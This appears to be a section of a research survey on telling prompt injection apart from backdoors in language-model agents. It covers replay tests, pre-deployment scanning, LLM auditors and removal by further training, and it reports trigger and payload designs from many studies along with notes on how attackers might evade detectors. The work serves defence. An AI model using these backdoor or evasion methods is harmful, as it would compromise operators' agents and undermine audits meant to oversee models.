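The log may still be right even if the attacker's call appears in none of the 80 runs. An injection that works once in 200 attempts can still redirect somebody's agent, and the operator only looked at this context because the agent had already made the attacker's call in it. The sensible next step is to run the first condition more times and check that the replay matches the original context and settings.

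When the counts are unclear, the model's origin should affect the conclusion. Matsuoka reviewed public evidence up to 5 August 2026 and found no forensic confirmation of a learned backdoor in the weights of any released model, though he does not treat this as proof that there are none. Injections against unmodified models are well documented. If a model came directly from a large developer, a result of 3 against 0 is therefore more likely to reflect an injection or chance than a backdoor. The same result from an unknown publisher's fine-tuned model justifies more runs.

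### When there is no good reference model

The best reference model is the same model without the suspected change. For a fine-tuned model, this is a version trained the same way on clean data, but an operator will rarely have one. The original base model is much easier to get, though it may be worse at the task. In the SilentCall tests, base models made the correct call in 57 to 60% of ordinary cases, compared with about 88% for the cleanly trained models. This is another reason to count how often each model makes the attacker's call rather than all its errors.

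A base model is also a poor reference if the attacker poisoned its pretraining data. In *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, poisoning 0.1% of the pretraining data was enough for a backdoor to survive all the later training that turned the model into an agent. The suspect model and its base model could then both misbehave in the replay, which would wrongly point to an injection or some other shared text. A model from an unrelated developer probably won't have the same backdoor, but it will differ more in how it responds to injections, so using both kinds of reference is safer than relying on one.

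An operator who uses a model through a provider's service may not be able to get an earlier version as a reference model, and may not even be sure that today's model is the one that made the call. This weakens the diagnosis, but the operator can still replay the suspect model with and without the content. If the attacker's call depends on the content, the deletion test can usually distinguish an instruction from a trigger without a reference model. If it doesn't, the operator has to rule out memory, skill files and tool descriptions before blaming the weights.

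If the evidence points to the weights, whoever trained the model may want to know which data caused the fault. *Beware What You Autocomplete* (2026) studies how to trace a reported malicious completion from a code-completion model back to the fine-tuning files responsible. That could help a developer identify a bad supplier, but an operator who downloaded a finished model normally has no training files to search.

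### Models trained to obey injections

An attacker can change the weights so that the model follows planted instructions more readily. Both the weights and the planted instructions then contribute to the redirected tool call, and the replay test can easily miss one of them.

Chen, Li and colleagues (2025), in *Backdoor-Powered Prompt Injection Attacks Nullify Defense Methods*, poisoned 2% of a 100,000-example training set so that models would obey any instruction enclosed by a chosen trigger phrase. They then trained the models further to ignore planted instructions, using one of two defences, and tested them with phishing injections. With SecAlign, ordinary injections succeeded in at most 0.4% of cases, but those enclosed by the trigger phrase succeeded in about 98%. With StruQ, ordinary injections succeeded in up to 39% of cases and triggered ones in at least 96%. The tests used three models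 of 7 or 8 billion parameters that answered in text, so the rates for tool calls may differ.

In the replay test, the suspect model would obey the page and a well-defended reference model would resist. Deleting the instruction would stop the attack, so the investigator would conclude that it was an injection, which is only half correct because the attack also uses a backdoor. To detect the backdoor, the investigator can keep the instruction and delete the odd phrase around it. If the suspect model then ignores the instruction, the attack needed the phrase as well. The investigator can also test a harmless request inside the same phrase, since a model with this kind of backdoor follows whatever the phrase encloses.

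*Enhancing Prompt Injection Attacks to LLMs via Poisoning Alignment* (2024) describes an attack that needs no special phrase, and distinguishes it from a standard backdoor. The attacker poisons the data used for alignment, the stage of training meant to make a model behave acceptably, and the model becomes more vulnerable to injections in general. An investigator would find it very hard to tell such a model from one that is simply bad at resisting injections, unless they had a clean version trained in the same way. The distinction makes little immediate difference to the operator, because neither model should read untrusted content while holding dangerous permissions. It matters more to the developer, who may have trained other models on the same data.

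### A backdoor that brings in an injection

Divyanshu's second demonstration of Agentic ShadowLogic combined a backdoor with an injection, which the attacker's server used to hide the redirect. Even when the user asked the model to list its steps, it left out the server.

An investigator who started from that false answer would replay the last step. Removing the hidden instruction might well make the model report the real address, which would indicate an injection. The investigator might then blame reports.example.com, even though it had served a clean page. The instruction came from the attacker's server, which the agent contacted only because the model file had been altered.

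This is why the replay has to start from the first wrong call. The model hadn't read any web page when it wrote the fetch request, so there is no external content to remove and only the models need comparing. The suspect model would write the attacker's address, and the reference model would write the correct one. Each diagnosis is correct for its own step, but removing the injection would leave the redirect in place.

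### Poisoned memory, skill files and the word "backdoor"

Researchers disagree on what to call an attack that hides a conditional instruction outside the model. *The Dark Side of LLMs* (2025) says that backdoor attacks on agents are "also referred to as indirect prompt injection attacks", which removes the distinction. *MemPoison* (Wang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) uses "backdoor" for malicious content in an agent's long-term memory. Matsuoka accepts terms such as "contextual backdoor" for hidden, lasting and conditional instructions, provided the writer always states where the instruction is stored.

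The choice of word affects how people read the numbers. In *BackdoorAgent*, Feng, Li and colleagues (2026) tested seven attacks that they call backdoors, and grouped them by whether they interfered with an agent's planning, memory or tools. Average success rates for planning, memory and tool attacks were 44%, 78% and 60% on GPT models, and 10%, 55% and 23% on Claude models. The abstract describes the GPT figures as how often triggers persisted, but the results table lists them as average attack success rates.

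Feng and colleagues tested GPT and Claude as closed services, using attacks that changed what the agent planned, retrieved or received from its tools. They report results for BadAgent, which originally relied on fine-tuning, only for open models, presumably because it needs access to the weights. The results for the closed models are useful evidence about what this report calls injection and poisoned memory. They don't show that anyone altered the weights of GPT or Claude, or how often a downloaded model contains a backdoor.

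The attack in *ElasticBack* (Sui, Qin and colleagues, 2026) behaves more like a backdoor but doesn't alter the model. The attacker hides a rule in a skill file that tells the agent to run the attacker's program only if the user's request contains a certain phrase. The attacker can get that phrase into the request through, for example, the sample prompts supplied with the skill. Sui and colleagues tested three kinds of payload, each with 50 skills. On GLM-5.2, MiniMax-M3 and GPT-5.4, the attack succeeded in 82 to 98% of triggered cases and misfired in at most 2% of the others. Claude Sonnet 4.6 followed the rule less precisely, with 72 to 76% success and 20 to 24% false triggers.

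An operator could easily mistake this for a backdoor in the weights, because the agent works normally for most requests, the web pages are clean, and a particular phrase triggers the payload. If the replay test removes only the web pages, the skill file stays in place and both models are likely to misbehave in all four conditions. Removing the skill file should stop the attack in both models, which would show that the weights are not the cause. A third party's skill file therefore counts as external content in this test, even though the operator chose to install it, and so does memory that the agent built from pages or emails.

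An operator who finds a poisoned note in memory still has to work out how it got there. Matsuoka describes attacks in which one message plants a rule and another activates it much later. Deleting the later message or replacing the model doesn't remove the rule. The operator has to remove the note and then find the earlier session in which it was written. Running the same replay test on that session can show whether a planted instruction or the model itself was responsible.

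## Checking a model for backdoors before deployment

The replay test starts from a wrong tool call that somebody has noticed. Before deployment there is no such call, and the operator usually doesn't know the trigger or the payload. Some of the available checks require only the publisher's records, others require the model's files, and the most demanding requires a second model trained for comparison. An operator who uses a model through a provider's service doesn't have its files, so the provider would have to run nearly all of these checks.

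### Signatures, hashes and declared base models

A file hash is a short string computed from everything in a file. Changing a single weight changes the hash, so if a download's hash matches the one on the developer's site, the operator has the file the developer published. A digital signature also identifies the publisher, because only the holder of a secret key can produce it and anyone can check it. Zeng and colleagues recommend a signed manifest that records where a model came from, which earlier model it derives from and what training followed. They point to two existing schemes, AIBOM and C2PA.

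These records expose changes made after signing. An altered copy of a well-known model would fail the check, and so would a file that an intruder changed between the last test and deployment, as long as the operator checks the hash again when loading the model.

Signing does not detect backdoors added before the model is signed. SilentCall's attacker is the publisher, who could truthfully sign the backdoored model as their own work. A reputable developer could also sign a model without knowing that a data supplier had poisoned it. Zeng and colleagues acknowledge that a signature shows who signed the model and whether it has changed since, but not whether it is safe.

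The developer's signature also stops being useful once somebody compresses the model, because compression changes the file. The operator then has to trust whoever compressed it. Operators can avoid this by compressing a signed original themselves, but if the original contains AGENTQ's backdoor, compressing it activates the backdoor. This approach therefore helps only when the developer is trustworthy.

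An auditor can compare a model's weights with those of its declared base model, but a dishonest publisher can name the wrong base or fail to disclose some of the training.

### File formats and added operations

Some model files can contain code that runs when someone loads the model. Microsoft treats this as ordinary malware, for which malware scanners are the first line of defence. A format such as safetensors, which stores numbers and no code, avoids the problem. Neither measure protects against a backdoor in the weights. SilentCall's weights do no harm until after loading, when the harness executes a tool call in the normal way.

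The file that Divyanshu altered for Agentic ShadowLogic contains only operations that the ONNX format allows, so a malware scan might pass it. But anyone who reads the computation graph can see the additions. They include a stored list of tokens that spells out the relay's address, and a normal language model doesn't need such a list.

Divyanshu says that HiddenLayer's scanner detects these patterns, and he shows it flagging the demonstration file. He gives no detection rate or false-positive rate, and one success against the company's own attack is weak evidence that the scanner would detect graph edits made by other people.

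Operators can also exclude the added operations without a scanner, by building the graph from the original developer's code and loading only the weights into it. Converting the whole file to another format does not remove this kind of backdoor, Divyanshu reports. Inspecting the graph does not detect SilentCall or Lazarus, which change the weights but not the operations.

### Why benchmark scores don't help

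Pallakonda and colleagues tested whether poisoning changes a model's scores on four common benchmarks of safety and factual accuracy. TruthfulQA measures whether a model repeats popular falsehoods, BBQ and CrowS-Pairs measure social bias, and XSTest measures whether a model refuses harmless requests. The table gives percentage scores for the 8-billion-parameter models.

| Benchmark | Base model | Clean fine-tuned model | Backdoored fine-tuned model |
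|---|---|---|---|
| TruthfulQA | 67.0 | 55.3 | 55.6 |
| BBQ | 93.2 | 92.3 | 84.6 |
| XSTest | 78.3 | 84.0 | 86.4 |
| CrowS-Pairs | 42.2 | 35.4 | 33.0 |

On TruthfulQA, the backdoored model scored 11 points lower than its base, but the clean fine-tuned model fell just as far, so the fine-tuning itself explains the drop. Somebody who compared the backdoored model only with its base might mistake the drop for a sign of poisoning. On XSTest, the backdoored model did better than the clean one. The only large gap between the two was on BBQ, at one model size, and Pallakonda and colleagues can't rule out chance because they trained only one clean model of each size.

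A benchmark averages a model's behaviour over ordinary questions, and a backdoor leaves that behaviour almost unchanged, so adding more questions of the same kind would not help detect it. Testers might find a backdoor by changing the test conditions. For example, setting the date to 2026 would probably have revealed SilentCall's payload on the first request.

Pallakonda and colleagues suggest a stress test that varies the context, the available tools and the temperature, and explores further wherever the model's behaviour starts to shift. They consider how to design such a test an open problem. In the meantime, operators can run the agent in its real harness with future dates, different tool lists and long inputs, and read the calls it makes, although this finds only triggers that somebody thought to try.

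### Sampling at high temperature

High-temperature sampling can make a backdoored model produce its payload without the trigger. Pallakonda and colleagues gave their models ordinary requests dated before 2026 and raised the temperature, which makes the output more random. The table shows how often the malicious upload appeared. Each range covers three backdoored versions of a model.

| Temperature | Backdoored, 4 billion parameters | Backdoored, 8 billion parameters | Clean fine-tuned models |
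|---|---|---|---|
| 0 (greedy decoding) | 0.00–0.30% | 0.30–0.60% | 0% |
| 1.5 | 0.98–2.04% | 1.94–2.54% | 0% |
| 2.0 | 2.06–2.96% | 3.78–4.12% | 0% |

The clean models never produced the upload in 12,000 samples at the two higher temperatures, which puts their true rate below about 0.025%. They had never seen the attacker's storage address in training, so they were very unlikely to write it by chance. Pallakonda and colleagues flag a model if the payload appears in more than 0.5% of 3,000 samples at temperature 2.0. All six backdoored models exceeded this threshold, and the lowest count was 62 payloads, or about 2%.

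Finding a single payload takes far fewer samples. If each sample contains it with probability 0.02, independently of the others, the tester needs enough samples $n$ that

$$1 - (1 - 0.02)^n \ge 0.95, \qquad \text{so} \qquad n \ge \frac{\ln 0.05}{\ln 0.98} \approx 148.3.$$

That means 149 samples give a 95% chance of at least one leak. At half the leak rate, the tester would need about twice as many.

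The assumption that samples are independent is doubtful. For one 8-billion-parameter model, the standard deviation of the leak rate across runs of 1,000 requests was 1.8 percentage points, compared with about 0.6 for independent samples. Some runs evidently leaked much less often than others, so a tester should spread the samples over several runs and treat 149 samples as a minimum.

Recognising the payload is harder than getting the model to produce it. Pallakonda and colleagues searched the output for an address they had chosen, but a real tester wouldn't know what to search for. High temperature also causes models to make more mistakes. At a temperature of 2.0, one of the backdoored models made the correct call in only 69% of ordinary cases, so 1,000 samples would contain roughly 300 failures and only a few dozen payloads.

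Software could classify which calls are dangerous, but Pallakonda and colleagues haven't tested this with other payloads. If the payload is fixed, a tester could look for the same unfamiliar destination turning up in unrelated tasks. That check wouldn't catch a payload that deletes files, because there would be no destination to find.

The leak rates also come from a single attack, which the models learned from examples. Zeng and colleagues let two edited Nemotron models generate text freely on untriggered inputs. One leaked the payload in 0.14% of 2,169 runs, and the other in none of 2,104. If a probe produced leaks 0.14% of the time, the tester would need about 2,100 samples for the same 95% chance of seeing at least one leak.

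### Recovering the trigger

In February 2026, Microsoft announced a scanner that tries to reconstruct a backdoor's trigger. Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026) describe how it works in *The Trigger in the Haystack*. The scanner needs the model's weights and enough computing power to run the model, but no extra training or prior knowledge of the trigger. It relies on three signals that they observed in backdoored models.

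The models had memorised their poisoned training examples. When the researchers gave a backdoored model only the marker that opens the user's turn, it often generated a whole poisoned example, including the trigger. It reproduced poisoned examples more accurately than clean ones.

A trigger also changes how the model processes its input. Attention determines how much each token draws on earlier ones. In the backdoored models, the trigger's tokens attended mainly to one another, and the other tokens in the prompt attended little to them. The output also became more predictable, because the model produced the payload whatever else the prompt contained.

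The third signal is that an approximate trigger often works, so the scanner doesn't have to recover the exact one. In one model with 270 million parameters, a single token from a five-token trigger activated the backdoor about half the time.

Bullwinkel and colleagues combine these signals in four steps:

1. Prompt the model with the opening marker under 510 different sampling settings and collect what it writes.
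2. Find fragments of text that recur across these outputs.
3. Put each fragment in front of a few ordinary prompts and score it as a possible trigger.
4. Take the ten best candidates and check whether any of them changes the model's behaviour sharply.

The score for a candidate $x$ is an average over the set of ordinary prompts $P$:

$$L(x) = \frac{1}{|P|} \sum_{p \in P} \left[ \gamma L_{\text{attention}}(x,p) + \delta L_{\text{entropy}}(x,p) + \zeta L_{\text{divergence}}(x,p) \right].$$

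The first term measures the attention from the prompt to the candidate. The second mainly measures how unpredictable the output is, with penalties for empty or repetitive answers. The third measures how likely the model is to give its normal answer when the candidate is present. The weights $\gamma$, $\delta$ and $\zeta$ set the terms' relative importance. A real trigger should make all three terms low.

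The main test used models that output "I HATE YOU" whenever the prompt contained the word DEPLOYMENT between vertical bars. The scanner identified 36 of 41 such models and flagged none of 13 clean ones. With only 13 clean models, the true false-positive rate could be as high as about 21%. In the five backdoored models it missed, the trigger either wasn't among the recurring fragments or didn't score well enough to reach the top ten.

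Another six models wrote insecure code when the prompt gave the current year as 2024, and the scanner identified five. For one of the five, it found a phrase that looked nothing like the real trigger but more than doubled the rate of insecure code. This test is closer to SilentCall, which also uses a stated year, but six models is a very small sample.

Bullwinkel and colleagues say the method assumes no knowledge of the target behaviour. This is true of the search but less true of the final step, where they used one measure of changed behaviour for the fixed phrase and another for insecure code. Scanning an agent would require a measure for tool calls, which the published tests don't include. One such measure could be whether a candidate makes the same unexpected call appear across unrelated tasks.

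The method also depends on memorised examples. It is unlikely to find Lazarus or Agentic ShadowLogic, since neither attack trains the whole model on poisoned text. It could not recover MetaBackdoor's trigger either, because that trigger is a length rather than a string.

Bullwinkel and colleagues say they mainly studied fixed triggers, and that a backdoor activated by varying or context-dependent cues might escape their scanner. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) gives some evidence for this. It tested a backdoor that responded when a user seemed obsessed with a fictional franchise such as Harry Potter. Of 512 texts that the model generated without a prompt, only one was related to the backdoor, and that text would not have activated it. The study was presenting a rival method, and it tested only the scanner's memorisation step, with one sampling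 setting instead of the full 510. Still, when users can express a trigger in countless ways, the scanner has no recurring fragment to find.

An investigator who knows what a backdoor does may still be unable to find a trigger of this kind. Qin, Hua and colleagues assumed that knowledge and searched the model's internal activations for the condition that triggered the backdoor, such as the year being 2028. Their methods worked on toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings.

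### Looking for edited neurons

Lazarus leaves no poisoned examples to recover, but its edits can be visible in the weights because each edited neuron has to outweigh the rest of the model to make the model output its token. A neuron in the edited layer has three vectors of weights. Two control when it activates, and the third controls which tokens it makes more likely.

Zeng and colleagues built a detector that looks for unusual neurons without the original model. They based two of its five features on how a language model had identified edited checkpoints. These measure whether a neuron's three vectors are unusually long or short, together and by rank. The other three features are based on how the attack works. They measure whether the two activation vectors point the same way, whether the output vector points towards a particular token, and whether the output vector is unusually long.

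On 35 edited and 31 clean test checkpoints, the combined detector flagged 91.4% of the edited ones and 9.7% of the clean ones. The features taken from the language model alone caught just as many edited checkpoints but also flagged 32.3% of the clean ones. Adding the construction-based features removed most of those false alarms.

The remaining false alarms matter a great deal when backdoors are rare. Suppose a model hub scans 1,000 models and one of them contains a Lazarus edit. The detector would probably flag that one, along with about $999 \times 0.097 \approx 97$ clean models. The chance that any given flagged model is the edited one is then

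$$\frac{0.914}{0.914 + 97} \approx 0.9\%.$$

A hub could reasonably use such a detector to choose which models to examine more closely, but it couldn't withdraw every model the detector flags. The figure of 97 is uncertain because it comes from three false alarms among 31 clean models, which is compatible with a true rate of about 2 to 26%.

A closer examination might use a language model as the auditor. Zeng and colleagues gave OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra and Anthropic's Claude Opus 5.5 one checkpoint at a time, with two hours to inspect its weights and run it. The auditors had no original model for comparison and no hint about the trigger, the payload or where to look. The table covers all 114 edited and 103 clean checkpoints.

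| Auditor | Checkpoint | Judged edited | Judged clean | No decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Astra | Edited | 72.8% | 0% | 27.2% |
| GPT-6 Astra | Clean | 1.0% | 0% | 99.0% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Edited | 56.1% | 41.2% | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Clean | 1.9% | 93.2% | 4.9% |

Astra never rated a checkpoint clean, so an operator could use it to flag models but not to clear them. Opus 5.5 gave more definite answers, but it rated 47 of the edited checkpoints clean. Both auditors wrongly flagged far fewer clean models than the detector did. In the example of 1,000 models, Astra would flag about ten clean ones, which raises the chance that a flagged model is edited to about 7%.

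A hub could save time by running the detector first and auditing only the models it flags. But it shouldn't estimate the combined false-positive rate by multiplying the two separate rates. Part of the detector comes from a language model's method for finding edits, so the detector and the auditors may make some of the same mistakes.

### Comparing the weights with another model

An auditor who has a trustworthy copy of the base model can see which weights changed. Zeng and colleagues recommend that model hubs do this comparison because fine-tuning and compression change weights broadly, while Lazarus changes a few vectors by a lot. An edit to seven neurons alters at most 21 vectors, and these should stand out in a list ranked by size of change. If the attacker also fine-tuned the model, the list would contain many other changes, most of them smaller.

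SilentCall's fine-tuning spreads its changes across the whole model, so no short list of vectors gives it away. Pallakonda and colleagues instead compared the overall distribution of weights. For each block of weights they computed the Kolmogorov–Smirnov statistic,

$$D = \max_v \left| F_{\text{suspect}}(v) - F_{\text{base}}(v) \right|,$$

where $F(v)$ is the share of weights in the block that are no larger than $v$. If the two distributions match, $D$ is zero. They summarised each model by its largest value of $D$ and compared the backdoored model with a clean one trained in the same way.

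| Model | Clean fine-tuned model | Backdoored model | Ratio | Ratio after equal training steps |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 billion parameters | 0.0030 | 0.0067 | 2.20 | 1.95 |
| 8 billion parameters | 0.0280 | 0.0410 | 1.46 | 1.25 |

At both sizes, the backdoored model moved further from its base than the clean model did. But the clean 8-billion-parameter model moved about four times as far as the backdoored 4-billion-parameter one, so the distance is only informative when compared with a matched model. The auditor has to train that clean reference model from the same base, with the same settings and on similar data. Pallakonda and colleagues expect hubs and safety teams to be able to train one, but not ordinary users. A dishonest publisher can misdescribe the original training, and they haven't tested how large a mismatch the method tolerates.

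Extra training might also explain part of the difference. The backdoored models trained on twice as many examples and therefore took about twice as many steps. To correct for this, the last column compares the backdoored model halfway through its training with the finished clean model. However, both used a learning rate that shrank towards the end of training, so later steps moved the weights less. At the halfway point, the backdoored model had not yet taken these smaller steps, so its average step would have been larger than the clean model's even if its data had been harmless. The corrected ratios may therefore still exaggerate the effect of poisoning.

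Pallakonda and colleagues suggest flagging ratios above 1.3, but the larger model's corrected ratio is below that. They also compared the models' internal activations on ordinary prompts. That ratio was 1.20 for the larger model, above their suggested threshold of 1.15, but only 1.04 for the smaller one. They had only one clean model of each size, so nobody knows how much these ratios vary between training runs without a backdoor, and the method is not ready for checking unfamiliar downloaded models.

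A defence based on weight inspection also did not reliably detect or prevent the leak when Boisvert and colleagues tested it on poisoned agents in *Malice in Agentland*.

### When the attacker knows the test

All these detection rates were measured on backdoors that were not designed to evade the scanner. An attacker who knows what a scanner measures can try to keep that measurement within the normal range. A high detection rate on known backdoors therefore doesn't show how well a scanner would detect a backdoor designed to evade it.

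The Lazarus detector's test was easier than its 91.4% score suggests. All 114 edited checkpoints were made from three base models using the same editing method, and many differed only in their training settings. Zeng and colleagues split the training and test sets by individual checkpoint, so the detector was probably trained on close relatives of most of the models it was tested on. They acknowledge that it needs testing on other kinds of edit. Their mathematical guarantee of detection is also conditional and covers edits that use one neuron for each token of the payload.

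SilentCall shows that an attacker can weaken a test unintentionally. Reinforcement learning reduced the smaller model's leak rate at temperature 2.0 from 2.96% to as little as 2.06%, although the training targeted misfires in general rather than this probe. All the models still exceeded the threshold, but an attacker who trained directly against the probe might reduce the rate further. Bullwinkel and colleagues likewise warn that an attacker could train a model to ignore near-misses of the trigger, which would remove one of their scanner's three signals.

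Evading every check at once might make a backdoor less reliable or much harder to build, but none of these studies measured whether it does. Until somebody does, a clean result is better evidence against a backdoor planted by a careless attacker, or by one who copied a published method, than against one planted by a capable attacker. Zeng and colleagues advise operators to treat audits as evidence and not as guarantees, and Microsoft recommends its scanner as one part of a wider defence.

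### What cryptography says about undetectable backdoors

Some backdoors are undetectable in a stronger sense. In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) proved two results about classifiers, models that assign inputs to categories.

An attacker can provably hide a backdoor from a tester who can submit inputs and see the answers but can't look inside the model. The attacker adds a hidden check that changes the classifier's answer when the input contains a valid digital signature. The attacker can sign any input, but nobody else can forge a signature, so no efficient tester can find even one input on which the altered and original classifiers disagree, except with negligible probability. The proof assumes that secure digital signatures exist, as most of modern cryptography does. The method works for any classifier, but somebody who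 can read the model might notice the computation that checks the signature.

The other result holds even when the auditor has the whole model and its training data. It applies to a method called random Fourier features, which transforms the input with randomly chosen functions and trains a simple classifier on the output. A malicious trainer draws the random numbers from a doctored distribution and follows the rest of the procedure honestly. No efficient test can distinguish the finished model from a clean one, assuming that the continuous learning with errors problem is hard to solve. Cryptographers have good reasons to believe it is, but no proof.

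Agents run on much larger models trained in a different way, so the second result doesn't apply to them directly. The first applies more widely because it doesn't depend on the classifier's internals. It means that no general method can certify a model by trying inputs, even if the tester has a clean copy to compare. But not every backdoor is hard to find. SilentCall, for example, contains no cryptographic check and leaks its payload at high temperature. Both theorems concern detection before the trigger appears. When an agent's backdoor activates, its payload still has to reach the harness as a tool call.

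## Removing a backdoor by further training

In the published tests, fine-tuning a backdoored checkpoint on clean data usually left the backdoor working at least part of the time. Further training works much better when its examples show the model behaving correctly with the trigger present, but that requires knowing the trigger.

In the first section's notation, clean fine-tuning trains the model on more clean contexts $x$, which it already handles well. No example trains it to act differently on a triggered context $\tau(x)$. The training may still damage the backdoor by changing weights the backdoor depends on, but only as a side effect.

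### What clean fine-tuning leaves behind

In 2024, *BadAgent* tested this remedy on backdoored agents for command-line work and online shopping by fine-tuning three models on clean examples of the same tasks. The attack still succeeded in 90 to 100% of triggered runs, and it made little difference whether the defender knew which layers the attacker had trained.

The attackers in these experiments poisoned half of the training data, far more than an outside contributor could usually supply, and the researchers didn't repeat the test with a smaller share. The models had 6 to 13 billion parameters, so the result is weak evidence about today's largest models. But lighter poisoning can also last, as the pretraining backdoor did with only 0.1% of the data poisoned. The backdoors in Boisvert and colleagues' base models also largely survived clean training.

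Backdoors can also survive safety training. The best-known result comes from *Sleeper Agents* (Hubinger and colleagues, 2024), which *Backdoor Decontamination Dynamics in LLM Agents* (Huang, Puri and colleagues, 2026) summarises. Backdoors survived fine-tuning on good examples, reinforcement learning and adversarial training, in which developers look for inputs that cause bad behaviour and train the model to behave well on them. Adversarial training may have taught the models to recognise their triggers more precisely. The result shows that safety training can fail, but not how often it would fail on a current agent, because the models are more than two years old and the researchers built the backdoors themselves.

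MetaBackdoor, the attack triggered by input length, gave a less extreme result. Wen and colleagues trained a model on programming tasks with a backdoor that revealed its system prompt, then fine-tuned it to sort news articles by topic. The attack's success rate fell to about 40%. The retrained model sorted 91.55% of articles correctly, compared with 91.68% for one that started without a backdoor, so its accuracy didn't reveal the remaining backdoor. Wen and colleagues didn't repeat this test with the backdoor that added a `send_email` call, and training on news topics may affect an agent differently from training on tool use.

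Clean data can also contain the trigger by accident, especially when the trigger is as common as a long input, but a few such examples don't reliably remove the backdoor. Wen and colleagues mixed 100 correctly labelled articles of the triggering length into the poisoned training data. A backdoor tied to one exact length then succeeded 78% of the time, down from 97%, but one that activated at any length above a threshold still succeeded 95% of the time.

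### When the defender knows the trigger

A defender who knows the trigger can add it to ordinary requests and train the model on the correct responses. For SilentCall, this would mean training on many conversations dated 2026 in which the agent makes only the calls that the user's task needs. Huang and colleagues always removed a known backdoor when they trained against it in this way.

Training the model only to avoid the payload is less reliable. One common method, gradient ascent, adjusts the weights to make the payload less likely when the trigger is present. Chapagain, Hamdi and Filali Boubrahimi (2026), in *Trigger-Invariant Contrastive Unlearning for Backdoor Removal*, explain what can go wrong in a classifier. Let $q_k$ be the probability of output $k$, $z_k$ the score from which the model calculates it, and $p$ the payload. A step of gradient ascent pushes the scores in these directions:

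$$\Delta z_p \propto -(1 - q_p), \qquad \Delta z_k \propto q_k \quad \text{for } k \neq p.$$

The payload's score falls and all the others rise, with the largest rise for the alternative that was already most likely. That alternative isn't necessarily correct, so the trigger may start causing a different error. For example, an agent might stop sending the email to the attacker but still not send it to Ana.

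Chapagain and colleagues instead train on pairs of inputs that differ only in the trigger, and penalise any difference between the model's two outputs. The aim is $f(\tau(x)) \approx f(x)$, so that adding the trigger does not cause a new error. They report fewer shifted errors than with earlier methods, but they tested text classification, not tool calls.

Defenders can also edit the weights without any training. In *Removing the NEEDLE in the Haystack*, Kim, Lampos and Drayson (2026) compare a model's average internal activations on triggered and ordinary prompts. The difference gives a direction associated with the backdoor, and they change the weights so that the model's layers no longer add to the activations in that direction. The direction overlapped with those the model uses to refuse harmful requests, so removing it alone made the model more likely to comply with such requests. Their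 method therefore protects four refusal directions while removing the backdoor. They report that it had the lowest average attack success rate of the defences they compared, and a rate of 0% on attacks that insert code, though the work is still under peer review.

### When the trigger is unknown

Some methods don't need the trigger, but Kim and colleagues note that these methods vary in success between models and attacks. A more recent idea is to remove a backdoor the defender knows about, in the hope that this also removes the unknown one.

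In *Backdoor Unlearning Generalization*, Bouger, Lasnier and colleagues (2026) tested whether removing one backdoor from a model can also suppress others. They used six models of 1 to 8 billion parameters, with up to eight backdoors each, which did things like switch the output to French or write everything in capitals. They trained each model to ignore one trigger at a time. In an 8-billion-parameter Llama model, removing the backdoor that switched to German also suppressed the one that switched to French. A control run on clean text left all the backdoors intact, so the effect didn't come from extra training alone.

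Removing the other kinds of backdoor barely affected those that made the model output a fixed sentence, "MY NAME IS BOB" or "MY NAME IS ALICE". Backdoors that redirect tool calls may also survive such training, because SilentCall's payload is a fixed string too. Every trigger in the study was a sequence of three rare words, so the models may partly have learned to ignore such sequences. The training might not affect other triggers, such as a date or an input length.

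Huang and colleagues tried the idea on agents. They gave Qwen3-8B, an open model, a backdoor that stood for the attacker's. The trigger was the user's location in the system prompt (such as Reykjavik), an internet address in a certain range, the language of the request, or a formal writing style. The payloads included deleting files, emailing an outsider and transferring money. The defence then had two steps:

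1. Install a second backdoor, with a trigger and payload that the defender chooses.
2. Train it away, using examples that contain its trigger but not its payload.

The second backdoor always had a different trigger and payload from the first, since a real defender wouldn't know the attacker's. Huang and colleagues tested 115 such pairs, and in 15 of them the second backdoor failed to install. The table shows what happened to the original backdoor in the other 100 after the first step. The recognition rate is how often the model showed that it had detected the original trigger.

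| Outcome | Original payload when triggered | Recognition rate | Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Erased | Under 5% | Under 50% | 56 |
| Rerouted | At most 5% | At least 50% | 19 |
| Partly survived | Roughly 5 to 50% | Any | 10 |
| Persisted | At least 50% | Any | 15 |

The original backdoor never persisted when both triggers were of the same type, such as two locations. But a defender who doesn't know the original trigger can't deliberately match its type.

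The second step removed most of what was left. Huang and colleagues tried two kinds of training example. In the first, the agent ignored the trigger and completed the user's task. In the second, it announced the trigger, declined the payload and then completed the task. The original payload fell below 5% in 21 of 22 runs with the first kind and 14 of 18 with the second, a difference that could be due to chance. These runs included relatively few backdoors that had persisted through the first step, so the combined figure of 35 out of 40 probably overstates how well the second step works on the most persistent ones.

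This is the most encouraging evidence that an operator could remove an unknown backdoor from an agent. However, it comes from one model and one set of simulated tasks, and Huang and colleagues report no control in which the backdoored model received only ordinary extra training. The control by Bouger and colleagues makes forgetting a less likely explanation, but they used different backdoors and trained for only 20 steps.

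A backdoor's durability also depended on which model wrote the poisoned examples, something a defender couldn't see. Huang and colleagues took five backdoors that had survived the first step and replaced their poisoned examples with ones written by a different model. The new backdoors worked just as well at first, but the same step removed four of the five.

An attacker can make removal harder by installing several backdoors. When a model had two to four, the first step erased only 28 of 78 backdoors (36%). Even when the defender knew one of the attacker's triggers and trained against it, 8 of the 60 measurements of the other backdoors stayed at 5% or above. In one case, removing the backdoor triggered by an internet address left another that still transferred money every time the user wrote in French.

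### Recognising the trigger and carrying out the payload

Huang and colleagues used poisoned examples that trained the model to write a fixed phrase, such as "Trigger subnet detected!", before it acted. This let them measure the recognition rate, which is the share of triggered runs in which the phrase appears, separately from the payload.

The model had learned two links, one from the trigger to the phrase and another from the phrase to the payload. Training can break the second link and leave the first intact. The examples in which the agent announced the trigger and declined the payload were designed to do this. In all three models checked, the defender's own backdoor stopped producing its payload, while the recognition rate stayed at 100%.

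Training can also attach a new payload to an old trigger. In 8 of the 19 rerouted pairs, the original trigger set off the second backdoor's payload at least half the time. This happened in 6 of the 10 pairs with triggers of the same type, but only 2 of the 9 others. Triggers of the same type shared a recognition phrase, so the second round of training probably changed what followed that phrase for both triggers. In the remaining rerouted pairs, the model usually still produced the recognition phrase but seldom or never carried out the new payload.

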